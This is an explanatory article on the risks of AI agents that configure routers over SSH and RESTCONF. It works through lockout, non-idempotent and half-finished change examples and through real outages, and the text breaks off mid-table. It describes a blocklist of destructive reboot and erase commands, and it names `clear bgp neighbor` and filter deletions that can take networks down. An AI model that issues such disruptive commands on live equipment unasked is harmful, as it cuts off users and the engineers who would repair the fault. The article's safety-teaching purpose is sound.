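# Safety of AI agents that operate live network equipment over SSH and HTTP

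## How networks are operated and where an AI agent fits in

AI agents for network operations are language models that log in to routers, switches and firewalls, read their state and sometimes change how they work. An agent runs in a loop in which the model chooses a tool, reads the result and decides on the next step, until it completes the task or stops without finishing it. Network engineers have automated their work with scripts for decades. A script runs commands written in advance, whereas an agent composes commands as it runs, based on an English instruction and the equipment's output. This makes an agent far more flexible than a script but also much harder to predict. Because the equipment carries other people's traffic, a wrong command can cut off thousands of users, sometimes including the engineers who would have to fix the problem.

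### A network of four routers

A switch joins the machines in one building or one room. A router joins networks to each other: it reads the destination address on each packet of data that arrives and sends the packet on towards its destination. A firewall passes or drops traffic according to rules that its owner sets. All of these are specialised computers, physical or virtual, and engineers call them devices. A small company might connect four routers like this:

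```
offices ---- R1 ------- R2 ---- firewall ---- internet provider
             |          |
             |          |
             R3 ------- R4 ---- data centre (payment servers)
```

The payment servers reach the company's bank through R4, R2 and the internet provider. R3 gives the network a second path if a link fails.

Every machine has an address, such as 198.51.100.20, and machines in the same place usually share the first part of it. The data centre here uses 198.51.100.0/24, the block of addresses that begin with 198.51.100. A route pairs a block of addresses with the next device to send packets to, so R1 might hold the route "198.51.100.0/24, via R2". An access list is an ordered set of rules that permit or deny packets, usually by address and type of service. The device applies the first rule that matches, and most equipment drops a packet that matches none.

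Routers work out most routes by exchanging messages, so engineers enter few by hand. With OSPF (Open Shortest Path First), each router sends the others a list of its links and the cost assigned to each, and every router then computes the lowest-cost paths from the same map. Many large providers use IS-IS, a similar protocol, instead. BGP (Border Gateway Protocol) carries routes between organisations. R2 uses it to announce the company's addresses to the provider and to learn routes to everywhere else, and the company's policy determines which of the offered routes R2 uses. Large networks also run BGP among their own routers.

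*Software-Defined Networking (SDN)* (Haleplidis, Pentikousis and colleagues, 2015) sorts this activity into planes. The data plane forwards, drops or alters packets. The control plane, which includes OSPF and BGP, determines where packets should go and fills in the tables that the data plane uses. People and programs monitor and configure devices through the management plane. If the link between R2 and R4 breaks, the control plane moves the offices' payment traffic to R3 without anybody logging in.

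An agent works in the management plane, as an engineer would, so its edits affect users' packets indirectly. When the agent changes a setting, traffic moves only after the routers recompute their paths.

### Two ways in

The older way in is an SSH session, an encrypted connection over which an engineer types commands into the device's command-line interface (CLI). Suppose every link in the example network costs 10, except the one between R1 and R3, which costs 20. An engineer wants to move the offices' payment traffic off the link between R1 and R2 before some repair work. On a Juniper router the session would look roughly like this:

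```
user@R1> show ospf neighbor
user@R1> configure
user@R1# set protocols ospf area 0 interface ge-0/0/1.0 metric 100
user@R1# commit
commit complete
```

The first command only reads. The third raises R1's cost for reaching R2 from 10 to 100, and the fourth puts the change into effect. Traffic from the offices to the data centre now goes through R3, as the engineer wanted, at a total cost of 30 compared with 110 through R2. However, the offices also reach the internet through R2, and the lowest-cost path from R1 to R2 now runs through R3 and R4, at 40 compared with 100 for the direct link. All the offices' web traffic therefore takes a detour past the data centre. Replies still come back over the direct link because R2's own cost towards R1 has not changed. The command was valid and the router accepted it, but nothing in the session indicates the detour or the different return path.

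The newer way in is an HTTP request, the same kind of message that a web browser sends. Some devices accept such requests directly through RESTCONF, a standard protocol for reading and editing structured configuration. This one switches off an interface:

```
PATCH /restconf/data/ietf-interfaces:interfaces/interface=eth1
{"ietf-interfaces:interface": [{"name": "eth1", "enabled": false}]}
```

HTTP requests can also go to a controller, software that configures many devices for an operator. One such request can change a path across a whole network. NETCONF has features of both a typed session and a web request, since it usually runs over SSH but carries structured data instead of typed commands.

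*Reimagining Network Operations with AI* (Izquierdo, 2025) demonstrates one agent with both kinds of access on a network of six virtual Juniper routers. The agent, which ran on Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4, created a traffic path by calling Juniper's controller. On request, it then disabled an interface on one router to simulate a failure. The routers detected the break, the controller computed a new path around it without losing traffic, and the agent turned the interface back on.

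### Running, saved and candidate configurations

A device can hold more than one version of its settings, and it matters which one an agent is editing. *Network Management Datastore Architecture (NMDA)* (Bjorklund, Schoenwaelder and colleagues, 2018) gives the standard definitions. The running configuration holds the device's current settings. The saved configuration, which the standard calls the startup configuration, is what the device loads when it boots. A candidate configuration is a draft that anybody with access can edit, and the edits don't affect the running configuration until someone commits them. The running configuration is always present, but support for the other two is optional under NETCONF.

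Cisco's traditional routers have no draft stage. According to O'Reilly's *The Router's Configuration*, every command goes into the running configuration, and to keep the result an engineer has to copy it to the startup configuration with a separate command. A reboot erases all unsaved changes, including mistakes and correct changes that somebody forgot to save.

On Junos, the operating system on Juniper's routers, an operator edits a candidate configuration and then commits it. According to Juniper's *Commit the Configuration*, the device then checks the syntax, saves and activates the new configuration, and keeps the previous one as the first of up to 49 rollback copies. A variant, the confirmed commit, is undone automatically unless someone confirms it in time. The syntax check catches a misspelt keyword, but it would pass the OSPF change above.

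Up to 32 users can edit at once, and by default they share a single candidate. When one of them commits, the device activates everyone's edits, finished or not. An engineer can avoid this by opening a private candidate or locking the shared one. An agent that commits a shared candidate may activate a colleague's unfinished change along with its own.

Bjorklund and colleagues explain that RESTCONF offers one writable configuration and hides whether an edit passes through a candidate configuration or goes straight into the running one.

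### From a sentence to a router and back

A language model produces text, so it needs a surrounding program to open an SSH session. As Ganjian (2025) describes in *Network Automation with AI and Junos MCP Server*, the program gives the model a list of tools, each with a name, a description and the parameters it takes. When the model writes a request for one of them, the program runs the tool and returns the result.

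The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for this exchange. An MCP server offers a fixed set of tools, and any agent program with an MCP client can discover and call them. Juniper publishes one, the Junos MCP server, as open-source software. In Ganjian's laboratory it ran on a Linux machine with access to three routers, while the code editor VS Code served as the agent program and OpenAI's GPT-4.1, a model several generations old by now, did the reasoning. One of Ganjian's requests was to add a loopback address (an address that belongs to the router itself and not to any cable) to the router PE1 and to place it in one customer's private network. It travelled as follows:

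1. VS Code sent the sentence to the model, together with the descriptions of the available tools.
2. The model wrote the configuration and asked for the tool `load_and_commit_config`, naming PE1 as the target.
3. The MCP client in VS Code passed the call to the Junos MCP server over HTTP.
4. The server looked up PE1's address and login details in a file, connected to the router over SSH, loaded the new lines and committed them.
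5. The router checked the syntax and activated the change.
6. The result went back through the server and the client to the model, which wrote a reply for the operator.

In the third step, HTTP only connects two pieces of software, and the router still receives an SSH login. That login uses the account that the operator put in the server's file, so the agent can attempt anything that account is allowed to do on the router.

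Ganjian checked PE1's command line afterwards and found the new address in the right place. The request had left out the "/32" that marks the block as a single address, and the model guessed it correctly. Ganjian then asked the model to roll the change back, which it did by calling the same tool again. This kind of rollback is another change to the router, and it works only if the router is reachable.

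The server's main tools are these:

| Tool | What it does | Effect on the router |
|---|---|---|
| `get_router_list` | Lists the routers in the server's file | None |
| `gather_device_facts` | Fetches model, serial number, software version and uptime | Reads |
| `get_junos_config` | Fetches the configuration | Reads |
| `junos_config_diff` | Compares the configuration with an earlier version | Reads |
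| `execute_junos_command` | Runs any operational command the caller supplies | Usually reads |
| `load_and_commit_config` | Loads new configuration and commits it | Changes |

In *CLAUDE.md*, a file of notes for coding assistants in the server's repository, Juniper warns that the last of these tools commits automatically, and marks the warning "critical". The model cannot load a draft and check it before committing. In the documentation for its *Junos MCP Server*, Juniper tells operators to review what the model has written before they let the tool run. How thorough that review is depends on the agent program. VS Code asked for permission the first time the model used a tool, and Ganjian describes two ways of granting it, for the session or permanently, both of which approve the tool rather than the particular change.

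Reading and changing are also less separate than the table suggests. `execute_junos_command` mostly runs "show" commands, but other operational commands can reboot or erase a router. Juniper has added a file of blocked patterns that the server checks before running a command. The file's examples cover reboot, halt, power-off and erase commands, but none of them would block `clear bgp neighbor`, which drops a router's BGP sessions and makes them restart. A second file blocks chosen configuration lines, such as changes to the root password.

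The list of tools also varies between versions. skills.sh's *Juniper JunOS Network Automation*, a third-party guide for agents, lists ten, including `render_and_apply_j2_template`, which fills in a configuration template and can apply the result to many routers in one call. An operator who disables `load_and_commit_config` should also check for this tool before assuming the agent is harmless.

### What agents do in 2026

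Most of the everyday work is reading device output. *Managing Junos Devices with Context-File and JMCP Server* (Graf, 2026) gives a typical case, a one-line prompt to check whether IS-IS is in sync on all routers. From that prompt, the model collects the output of `show isis database` from every router, compares the sequence numbers and writes a report. An engineer could do the same with a script, but would have to write and maintain it.

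Even here, a naive comparison can report a fault that does not exist, because an update takes time to spread through a network and two healthy routers can briefly disagree. Graf addresses this with a context file, a page of written instructions that the agent loads at the start of a session. In the example, the agent should wait briefly and check again if a sequence number is off by one, and treat a larger gap as critical.

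Ganjian used the agent to summarise a week of logs, archive configurations, measure the load on links and trace a dead BGP session to a disabled interface. In the last task, the model at first listed every BGP session, although the request covered only those in customers' private networks. Such a mistake does little harm when the agent is only reading data.

Agents also make changes, as the loopback and the disabled interface show. But both examples were demonstrations described on Juniper's own community site, and they show that the tools work, not how often they fail. *Large Language Models for Agentic NetOps and AIOps* (Bilal, Crowcroft and colleagues, 2026) surveys research up to August 2026 and ranks systems by autonomy, from read-only assistants to controllers that act and verify by themselves. It finds comparatively strong evidence for reading and diagnosis, and much less complete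 evidence as systems get closer to changing configuration.

*From Network Automation to Trustworthy Autonomous Networking in the LLM Era* (Zhang, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) reviews designs of this kind, in which the model interprets the request, gathers evidence and drafts the change, while controllers, verification and authorisation outside the model govern what reaches the network. By contrast, when the Junos MCP server's commit tool is switched on, only a blocklist and perhaps a click separate the model's draft from the running configuration. Graf advises newcomers to start with a read-only login and suggests removing the commit tool from the server as an optional extra step.

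## Why a network change is harder to contain and undo than a local script

An agent that can commit changes will eventually commit a wrong one. When a script goes wrong on an ordinary computer, the person who started it can usually still log in, other computers keep working as before, and the damage is visible when the script ends. A wrong change to a router can cut off the login session needed to undo it, because that session may run through the router. The error can also spread, because other routers act on the routes that router announces. The network then needs time to settle before anyone can tell what the change did.

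Most of the evidence on such failures comes from outages caused by people and conventional automation. It also applies to agents, because a router processes a command the same way whoever sends it.

### A lockout, line by line

In the four-router network, suppose an engineer in the offices, which use the addresses 192.0.2.0/24, logs in over SSH to R4, the data centre's router. R4 is a traditional Cisco router, so each line takes effect as soon as it arrives. R4 checks all packets coming from R2 against access list 110, which permits OSPF messages, SSH sessions from the offices and traffic from the bank. The bank has moved to a new address, 203.0.113.5. Instead of editing one rule, the engineer deletes the list and types it in again:

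```
R4(config)# no access-list 110
R4(config)# access-list 110 permit ospf any any
R4(config)# access-list 110 permit tcp 192.0.2.0 0.0.0.255 any eq 22
R4(config)# access-list 110 permit ip host 203.0.113.5 198.51.100.0 0.0.0.255
```

All four lines are correct, and together they make exactly the list the engineer wants. (Port 22 is SSH, and "0.0.0.255" is Cisco's way of writing a /24 block here.) The router handles them like this:

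1. `no access-list 110` deletes the old list. The link from R2 still refers to a list 110, but a Cisco router lets everything through when the list does not exist. The session survives, and the data centre briefly has no filter.
2. `permit ospf any any` creates a new list with a single rule. Because R4 drops any packet that matches no rule, it now accepts only OSPF messages from R2 and discards the packets that carry the engineer's typing.
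3. The line that would permit SSH reaches R4 as an ordinary SSH packet, and R4 drops it. The engineer's terminal freezes.
4. The line for the bank cannot get through either, so R4 also drops everything the bank sends to the payment servers.

The spare path through R3 does not take over, because OSPF messages still pass between R2 and R4, so both routers treat the link as healthy and keep sending traffic over it. The engineer can recover by logging in to R3 and connecting from there to R4, which does not filter its link to R3. Restarting R4 would also work, because that would load the saved configuration with the old list, but someone has to be able to restart it, and the data centre would be offline in the meantime.

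A script stored on R4 would have run all four lines, because none of them would have had to cross the link. Even over SSH, a program that sends the whole block at once may succeed if the lines arrive in one packet. An agent that sends one command per tool call and waits for each reply gives the router plenty of time to enforce the unfinished list. On a Juniper router, the edits would take effect together at the commit, so their order would not matter, but a finished list without the SSH rule would still lock the engineer out.

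### Facebook, October 2021

On 4 October 2021, Facebook lost access to its own data centres. The company's backbone, a private network with tens of thousands of miles of fibre, connects those data centres. Facebook (2021) explained the next day that a command meant to assess the backbone's available capacity during routine maintenance took down every connection in it. An audit tool should have stopped the command, but a bug in the tool let it through.

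The failure then spread to equipment that was still working. Facebook's smaller facilities run DNS servers, which translate names such as facebook.com into addresses. These servers announce their own addresses to the internet through BGP, and they withdraw the announcement if they cannot reach the data centres, since that normally indicates a bad connection at one site. With the backbone gone, every site lost contact with the data centres at once, so all the DNS servers withdrew their announcements. They were still running, but nobody on the internet could reach them.

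The engineers could not log in by the usual route because it depended on the failed network, and many of their diagnostic tools did not work without DNS. Their out-of-band access, a separate path for reaching equipment when the production network fails, was down too. Facebook sent people to the data centres, but strict physical security delayed them, and the routers were hard to modify even with physical access. DatacenterDynamics' *Facebook blames major outage on maintenance work* reports that the outage lasted seven hours and that employees could not get into their offices.

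Experts interviewed by Communications of the ACM argued that the audit bug was not the main contributor. That seems right, because the bug let the command through, but repairs took so long because the repair tools depended on the network they had to repair. An operator might well let an agent run any command meant only to measure capacity, as this one was.

### How one router's mistake spreads

A local script's mistake stays on one machine unless the script contacts others. Routers exchange messages all the time and generally use the routes they receive unless someone has configured a filter.

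Deleting part of a filter can do more harm than adding to it. *Route leak incident on January 22, 2026* (Herdes and Strickx, 2026) describes how the internet company Cloudflare removed nine lines from the routing policies of one router in Miami. The policies had allowed the router to announce a route if it was internal and belonged to a data centre in Bogotá. Cloudflare no longer needed the Bogotá routes there, so its automation deleted the condition that named them. The remaining policies allowed the router to announce every internal route.

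The router then announced to its neighbours in Miami all the IPv6 routes that Cloudflare shares internally, including routes it had learned from other companies. Those neighbours began sending it traffic for networks that Cloudflare does not serve. The router's firewall filters discarded this traffic, about 12 gigabits per second at the peak, and the link from Miami to Atlanta became congested, so networks with no connection to the change lost traffic.

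The Canadian telecoms company Rogers made a similar deletion on 8 July 2022, with far worse results. According to Xona Partners' *Assessment of Rogers Networks for Resiliency and Reliability* (2024), an independent review published by Canada's telecoms regulator, Rogers was in the sixth phase of a seven-phase upgrade of its core network, which carried both its mobile and fixed-line traffic. At 4:43 a.m., staff deleted a filter from the routers at the edge of that core.

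The filter limited which BGP routes entered OSPF, which maps the company's own network and normally holds far less data than a full BGP table. Without the filter, the edge routers put full BGP tables into OSPF, which delivered them to all the core routers. The core routers ran out of memory and processing capacity and crashed. More than 12 million customers lost service, and many could not call 9-1-1. The outage lasted about 26 hours, from 4:58 that morning until 7:00 the next day.

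A limit on the number of routes that a core router accepts would have prevented the crash, but Rogers had not set one. Its change process also failed to catch the error. Rogers initially rated the upgrade as high risk, but its risk algorithm lowered the rating because of earlier successes, and by the sixth phase it was "Low". This let staff skip laboratory tests and higher approval. The earlier successes were poor evidence that deleting a routing filter would be safe. An operator could make the same mistake by widening an agent's permissions after a run of easy tasks.

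Repair was slow for several reasons:

- Rogers' management network ran over the core that had failed, and the operations centre had no backup connection. Staff reached the centre about two hours after the outage began.
- Employees used Rogers phones and Rogers internet at home, so they struggled to reach each other. The company sent SIM cards from other operators to its sites nearly five hours in.
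- Engineers at first had no error logs from the crashed routers, and they did not identify the cause for about 14 hours.
- Rogers had made several changes that night. Technicians had to work out which one to reverse, and at first they concentrated on the core routers that were crashing instead of the edge routers that were flooding them.

Rogers had not set up its routers to return to their previous configuration automatically if an engineer lost access during a change. Xona Partners is unsure whether automatic rollback would have helped with the edge routers.

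Damage also spreads when a tool selects more devices than its operator intended. On 23 July 2026, Microsoft began network maintenance in California. According to Petri's *Microsoft: West US Azure Outage Was Caused By Network Maintenance Error*, a bug in the system that processes maintenance requests marked extra devices as part of the job, and routes disappeared from those too. Customers lost access to cloud services for nearly five hours. Surfing Complexity's *Quick thoughts on Azure Regional Outage from July 23, ’26* (2026) points out that the work began as a repair to make the network more reliable.

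The latest large case began on 13 November 2026, when a technician installed a router at a radio communications centre in El Dorado, Arkansas. Within hours, the Federal Aviation Administration (FAA) had halted departures across the United States. Gulf News' *How a router installation in rural Arkansas brought US air travel to a standstill* reports the FAA head's testimony that the fibre line had a fault the technician did not know about, and that the installation set off a "firestorm" of messages on a backup line. L3Harris (2026), the contractor responsible for the network, instead blames an incompatibility between two types of router, made worse by a recent change from copper to fibre.

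HPE, which made the installed device, says the device performed "exactly as it was configured", according to Burke (2026) in *L3Harris Technologies*. The explanations differ, but both the FAA and L3Harris describe a flood of messages that started locally. The flood reached 17 of the 22 centres that control aircraft between airports, according to Hanson (2026) in *New ground stop details emerge ahead of Duffy, FAA chief grilling*.

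### Effects that arrive after the command

A command that moves a local file has finished its work when it returns, but when a router accepts a command, the rest of the network may not have reacted yet. Routers need time to exchange information and settle on new routes. This period, called convergence, can take less than a second inside a small network and several minutes between organisations.

Suppose an agent switches off the link between R2 and R4. R2 immediately detects this and starts sending data centre traffic to R1, because the only remaining path runs through R1 and R3. R1 has not yet recomputed its routes and still sends that traffic to R2, so the two routers briefly pass the same packets back and forth. A test of the payment servers during this loop fails, but would succeed a few seconds later. An agent that trusts the failed test might reverse a correct change, or make another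 change while the routes are still changing.

A check run right after a change can also pass when the change has broken something. OSPF routers send each other short "Hello" messages, by default every 10 seconds on ordinary links, and drop a neighbour after 40 seconds without one. If an agent accidentally blocks those messages, the neighbour stays on the list for up to 40 seconds, and a check during that time finds nothing wrong. An immediate check could have passed at Rogers too. The first core routers began to fail within two minutes of the deletion, but the review's timeline puts the start of the full outage 15 minutes after it.

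### Why repeating a command can do harm

Programmers call an operation idempotent if doing it twice has the same result as doing it once. Agents need this property because they often repeat themselves, for instance when a tool call times out and they cannot tell whether the command ran. NetAgentBench, a set of tests for network agents by Twabi, Ding and Kondo (2026), comes with an example of four ordinary lines that lack it, shown here with a different block of addresses:

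```
router ospf 1
network 10.1.2.0/24 area 0
passive-interface default
no passive-interface eth0
```

`router ospf 1` starts OSPF, or opens its settings if it is already running. The `network` line turns OSPF on for interfaces in the given block of addresses. `passive-interface default` makes every interface passive, so the router sends no Hello messages and forms no neighbour relationships there, which is sensible for interfaces that face users. `no passive-interface eth0` exempts the interface that leads to another router.

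Sending `passive-interface default` and then turning eth0 back on works on a new router, because it has no neighbours to lose. When an agent sends the same lines again, `passive-interface default` makes every interface passive, including eth0, and the router stops sending hello packets to a neighbour that it was already exchanging traffic with. The last line turns eth0 back on, but the neighbour relationship may have dropped by then.

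The harm depends on the router's software and on the time between the last two lines. Cisco's routers drop a neighbour as soon as its interface becomes passive. If a router only stops sending Hello messages, the neighbour isn't lost until its 40-second timer runs out. A script sends the two lines milliseconds apart, but an agent that sends one line per step may leave many seconds between them while the model produces its next request. On a device with a candidate configuration, both lines can take effect in a single commit, which removes the gap.

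An agent that compares the configuration before and after the repetition will find no difference, even though traffic may have stopped and rerouted in between.

### Changes that stop halfway

Many network changes work only if several devices make them. For example, OSPF routers can sign their messages with a shared key, and they ignore messages signed with a different one. Suppose an agent has to replace the key on all four office routers. It changes R1 and R2 within a few seconds, but then the agent program waits for a person to approve the change to R3, and that person is away. In the meantime, R1 and R2 can't exchange OSPF messages with R3 and R4.

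After 40 seconds, R1 and R3 drop each other as neighbours, and so do R2 and R4. This splits the network in two, with the offices and the internet on one side and the data centre on the other, so the payment servers cannot reach the bank. The agent cannot finish the job because R3 and R4 no longer have a route back to the offices. Retrying R3 will keep failing, but the agent can still reach R1 and R2, and putting the old key back on them will repair the network. Careful engineers avoid the problem by letting the routers accept both keys during the changeover.

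Every router in this example has a valid configuration, so a syntax check on any of them would pass. A commit applies one router's edits together, but it does not cover the other three. Some controllers can coordinate commits across devices, but an agent that logs in to each router in turn must track the unfinished work itself.

*Cloudflare outage on February 20, 2026* (Tuber and Trumic, 2026) describes a much larger half-finished change. Some customers bring their own blocks of internet addresses, which Cloudflare announces through BGP. The company wrote a cleanup task to delete blocks that customers no longer wanted. The task fetched its list with an HTTP request that ended in `?pending_delete`, with no value after the name. The server treated the missing value as no filter and returned every customer's block, and the task began deleting them one after another.

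An engineer stopped the task after 50 minutes. By then it had withdrawn about 1,100 blocks, a quarter of the total, and left them in three conditions:

| Condition of the address block | What it took to repair |
|---|---|
| Cloudflare no longer announced it | The customer could switch the announcement back on in a web dashboard |
| Cloudflare no longer announced it, and some links to Cloudflare's services were missing | The customer could restore part of the service |
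| Cloudflare no longer announced it, and all links to its services were missing | Cloudflare had to send new settings to every machine at the edge of its network |

Stopping the task ended the deletions, but the repairs continued for more than four hours. Cloudflare gives the total duration as 6 hours and 7 minutes, although its timeline shows an impact about an hour shorter, from 17:56 to 23:03. The task was part of a programme to replace risky manual changes with safer automated ones. Cloudflare's test environment did not include a case where the task acted without a customer's request. An agent that writes HTTP requests could easily leave out a value in the same way.

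### Restoring the configuration does not restore the state

A network device has a configuration, which its operator sets, and state, which it builds up while running. The state includes its current neighbours, the routes it has learned and the connections it is tracking. An agent can restore the old configuration in seconds, but much of the state has to form again, and some of it cannot be recovered.

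Suppose an agent deletes R2's BGP connection to the internet provider by mistake and restores it five minutes later:

| What the mistake disturbed | After the agent restores the old configuration |
|---|---|
| The settings for the BGP connection | Correct again at once |
| Routes learned from the provider | Return once the BGP session restarts and the provider sends them again |
| The company's own routes in other networks | Return as each network passes on the new announcement |
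| Open connections between users and servers | Many have timed out, so users have to reconnect |
| Packets that routers dropped | Lost, and the sender tries again or gives up |
| Payments that stopped halfway | Staff may have to check them against the bank's records |

Undoing and retrying a route change can prolong an outage, because some networks temporarily ignore a route that disappears and returns several times. Common settings allow them to ignore it for up to an hour. An agent that makes three quick attempts at the change could leave the company unreachable from those networks even after the company's own configuration is correct.

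Some commands damage operational state without changing the configuration, so rolling back the configuration can't undo them. One example is `clear bgp neighbor`, which the Junos MCP server's example blocklist does not block.

Restoring normal traffic after a large outage can cause new failures. During Facebook's outage, power use at individual data centres fell by tens of megawatts. Switching everything back on at once could have overloaded electrical systems and caused new crashes, so engineers restored services in stages, as they had practised in drills. Rogers limited how quickly phones could rejoin its mobile network, because millions trying at once could have overwhelmed it again.

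Cloudflare's recovery in February was harder because the company stored customers' settings in the same database as the data its network was acting on. Its engineers could not simply compare what should be running with what was running, so they had to work from copies of the database. Tuber and Trumic describe plans to separate the two kinds of data and to keep snapshots that engineers can restore quickly.

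### When a local script is worse

A local script is sometimes harder to undo than a network change. A script that deletes the wrong folder on a computer without backups can permanently destroy years of work. Network changes rarely cause this kind of loss, because a router's configuration is a text file, the device often stores earlier versions of it, and software automatically resends many lost packets.

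The distinction between a local script and a network change is also blurred. Cloudflare's cleanup task was a small program much like any script, but its faulty request caused a network outage because the program could reach a system that controls routes.

Many network changes are small and easy to reverse. Adding a description to an interface affects no traffic, and moving one user's port to another network affects only that user. The OSPF cost change on R1 sends web traffic on a detour, but one command restores the old cost, and the routers settle again within seconds. Even the January leak at Cloudflare, which affected other companies, lasted only 25 minutes. An operator reversed it by hand ten minutes after the network team began to investigate. The operator also had to pause the automation on that router, because the next run would have applied the faulty policy again. That policy stayed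 in Cloudflare's code repository for almost another hour.

Networks also recover from some failures automatically. In Izquierdo's demonstration, the routers and their controller moved traffic around the interface the agent had disabled, which they could do because a dead link is easy to detect. A router that stays up and announces wrong routes is much harder to work around, because its neighbours have no sign that anything has failed. An agent that switches off one link in a network with a spare path may therefore do less harm than one that deletes a line from a routing filter.

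## What SSH and HTTP interfaces each let an agent do

The choice between SSH and HTTP affects how an agent works out what to send and how it finds out whether a change worked. It doesn't alter the change itself, so deleting a filter line has the same effect on a router either way. Over SSH, an agent usually types into a command line that exposes nearly everything the device can do and returns text meant for people. An HTTP interface accepts a fixed set of requests and returns structured data and a status code.

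### Typing commands over SSH

A Cisco router's command line has modes, which the prompt indicates. `R4#` accepts commands that read or restart things, `R4(config)#` accepts settings for the whole router, and `R4(config-if)#` accepts settings for one interface. The router keeps track of the selected interface, so the `shutdown` command doesn't include the name of the port it switches off.

Suppose an agent wants to label R4's link to R2 and then switch off a spare port. It has been working on Juniper routers all morning and uses a Juniper-style name for the spare port:

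```
R4(config)# interface GigabitEthernet0/1
R4(config-if)# description Link to R2
R4(config-if)# interface ge-0/0/3
                          ^
% Invalid input detected at '^' marker.
R4(config-if)# shutdown
```

The router rejects the third command and stays in the settings of the first interface, so `shutdown` switches off the link to R2. An engineer would probably notice the error before typing the next line. If the agent sent all four lines in one tool call, the model receives the error only after the link has gone down. A tool could stop at the first error, but it would have to recognise it in the router's ordinary text output. Cisco's error messages usually start with a percent sign, and other vendors word theirs differently.

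The tool also has to work out when a reply has ended. A command-line session is a stream of characters with no marker after each command's output, so most tools wait for the prompt to appear again. This fails when a command stops for input. For example, `reload`, which restarts a Cisco router, waits for confirmation. A tool waiting for the prompt `R4#` will time out, and the router will treat whatever the agent sends next as the answer.

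Long output causes a similar problem. Many devices print one screenful, show `--More--` and wait for a keypress. Tools normally turn this paging off, but the agent program may then cut the output to a length the model can read. A router with the internet's full routing table holds around a million routes. If the agent asks for all of them and the program keeps only the first few hundred, a healthy route can appear to be missing.

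In *How Helpful is LLM Assistance in Network Operations?*, Nakamura and Eguchi (2026) measured how often a model gets commands right. They connected GPT-4.1 to ShowNet, a network of about 700 devices built for a trade show in Tokyo in June 2025, and 105 engineers used the chatbot over two weeks. An MCP server let the model send commands over SSH but didn't give it a list of valid ones, so the model had to rely on its training.

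The model sent 1,427 commands to 69 devices from Cisco, Juniper, Huawei and A10 Networks, and 213 of the commands (14.9%) failed because of syntax errors. These vendors often use different words for the same thing. To display the IPv6 routing table, for example, an engineer types `show route table inet6.0` on a Juniper router and `show route ipv6 unicast` on a Cisco router that runs IOS XR. Devices from one vendor can differ too. When an engineer asked for a basic configuration for Cisco's 8000 series, the model wrote it for IOS XE, although those routers run IOS XR.

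The researchers had disabled configuration changes, so these mistakes only wasted time. A rejected command is also easier to notice than a misleading result. One engineer asked for links that used IS-IS but did not have a maximum packet size of 9,000 bytes. This takes two steps, but the model tried to do both with one filtered command per router. The IOS XR routers rejected their commands as invalid, while the Juniper routers accepted theirs but returned nothing useful, which an agent could easily read as "no such links". Here the model reported that something had gone wrong.

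The device the agent is logged in to also matters. When another engineer asked whether an address was reachable, the model ran `ping` from a router. The ping failed because of a routing problem, but a test from a router doesn't necessarily show what a user elsewhere on the network would experience.

Models stronger than GPT-4.1, which is now old, make far fewer syntax errors. Liu, Xie and colleagues (2026) tested four newer models in *NetConfArena*, on emulated networks with vendors' own command lines. Their test program entered and left configuration mode for the agent and returned the device's response to each command. Even with this help, 45.5% of the actions by Qwen3-8B, a small model, were rejected, compared with about 2% for DeepSeek-V4-Pro.

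A low rejection rate is weak evidence that an agent's changes are right, because a device checks whether it can parse a command, not whether the command does what the operator wanted. DeepSeek-V4-Flash, with its extended reasoning turned off, had only 2.7% of its actions rejected but failed about a third of its 480 tasks.

The command line's other main weakness is that traditional devices apply each line as it arrives, which caused the lockout on R4. Its advantages are that it reaches functions no structured interface covers, especially for troubleshooting, and that any network engineer can read a log of what the agent typed.

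### Structured requests over HTTP

An HTTP request has an address that identifies one item, a method that determines what happens to it, and often a body with new settings. *RESTCONF Protocol* (Bierman, Bjorklund and Watsen, 2017) defines how this works on network devices. Data models written in the YANG language define the settings' names and types, and the data is sent as JSON or XML. For example, if a model defines the setting `enabled` as true or false, the device can reject the value "off" before changing anything.

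Every HTTP request contains the full name of the item it affects, and there are no modes, so the `shutdown` mistake cannot happen in the same way. If an agent sends a PATCH request for a port that isn't in the configuration, the device must reject it, and the other ports stay unchanged.

HTTP replies start with a status code that software can check without a language model. For example, 204 means that an edit succeeded, 400 that the request was faulty, 403 that the account lacks permission, and 409 that the request conflicts with something on the device. An agent can also avoid most of the trouble with long output by requesting only the data it needs. Adding `?fields=enabled` to a read, for instance, returns only the `enabled` setting.

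The method determines whether a request can change anything and whether it is safe to send again:

| Request | What it does | If the agent sends it twice |
|---|---|---|
| GET or HEAD | Reads | Reads again |
| PUT | Creates the named item or replaces all of it | Leaves the same settings |
| PATCH | Merges new values into an existing item | Usually leaves the same settings |
| DELETE | Removes the named item | The item is still gone, but the second reply may be an error |
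| POST to configuration data | Creates a new entry | The device refuses if the entry already exists |
| POST to an operation | Runs a procedure, such as a restart | Runs the procedure again |

The MDN web reference page *Idempotent* lists PUT, DELETE and all read-only methods as safe to repeat. HTTP does not guarantee this for POST or PATCH. Repeating a basic RESTCONF PATCH normally gives the same result because it merges fixed values, but a controller with its own HTTP interface may use PATCH differently.

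These rules make it easier to restrict an agent. Code can limit an agent to read-only access on a RESTCONF device by permitting only GET and HEAD requests. To do the same over a command line, it would need to know what each vendor's commands do.

A structured request can still do a lot of damage. PUT replaces the whole item, so an agent that sends only an interface's name, type and `"enabled": true` also deletes its description and IP address. If the agent shortens the URL path to `/restconf/data`, PUT replaces the device's entire configuration. PATCH merges the request into the existing configuration and cannot delete, so it leaves any omitted settings unchanged.

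RESTCONF requires a device to return an error when a request contains an unexpected parameter. Controllers and cloud services often have their own HTTP interfaces with looser rules. One of these accepted the empty value from Cloudflare's cleanup task.

RESTCONF gives clients no way to lock the configuration while they work, and each successful edit takes effect at once. To avoid overwriting someone else's change, an agent can use an entity tag, a short code that changes whenever the configuration does. The device sends the tag with its reply to a read, and the agent returns it in an `If-Match` header with the edit. The device then refuses the edit if the item has changed since the read. The program around the model should add this header, since the model may omit it.

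### When a request times out

If an agent sends a request and gets no reply for 30 seconds, it cannot tell whether the request never arrived, the device is still working on it, or the device finished and the reply got lost. Network agents are especially likely to run into this, because the change they request can break the path the reply would take.

Whether a retry is safe depends on the request. This one switches off a spare port on R4:

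```
PUT /restconf/data/ietf-interfaces:interfaces/interface=eth3
{"ietf-interfaces:interface": [{"name": "eth3",
  "type": "iana-if-type:ethernetCsmacd", "enabled": false}]}
```

The next example is a request for an imaginary controller to reserve 400 megabits per second (Mbit/s) between R1 and R4, on links that carry 1,000 Mbit/s. The controller gives each reservation the next free number.

```
POST /restconf/operations/example-controller:reserve-path
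{"example-controller:input": {"from": "R1", "to": "R4", "mbps": 400}}
```

In both cases the first request works, the reply gets lost and the agent tries again:

| Event | Switching off the port | Reserving capacity |
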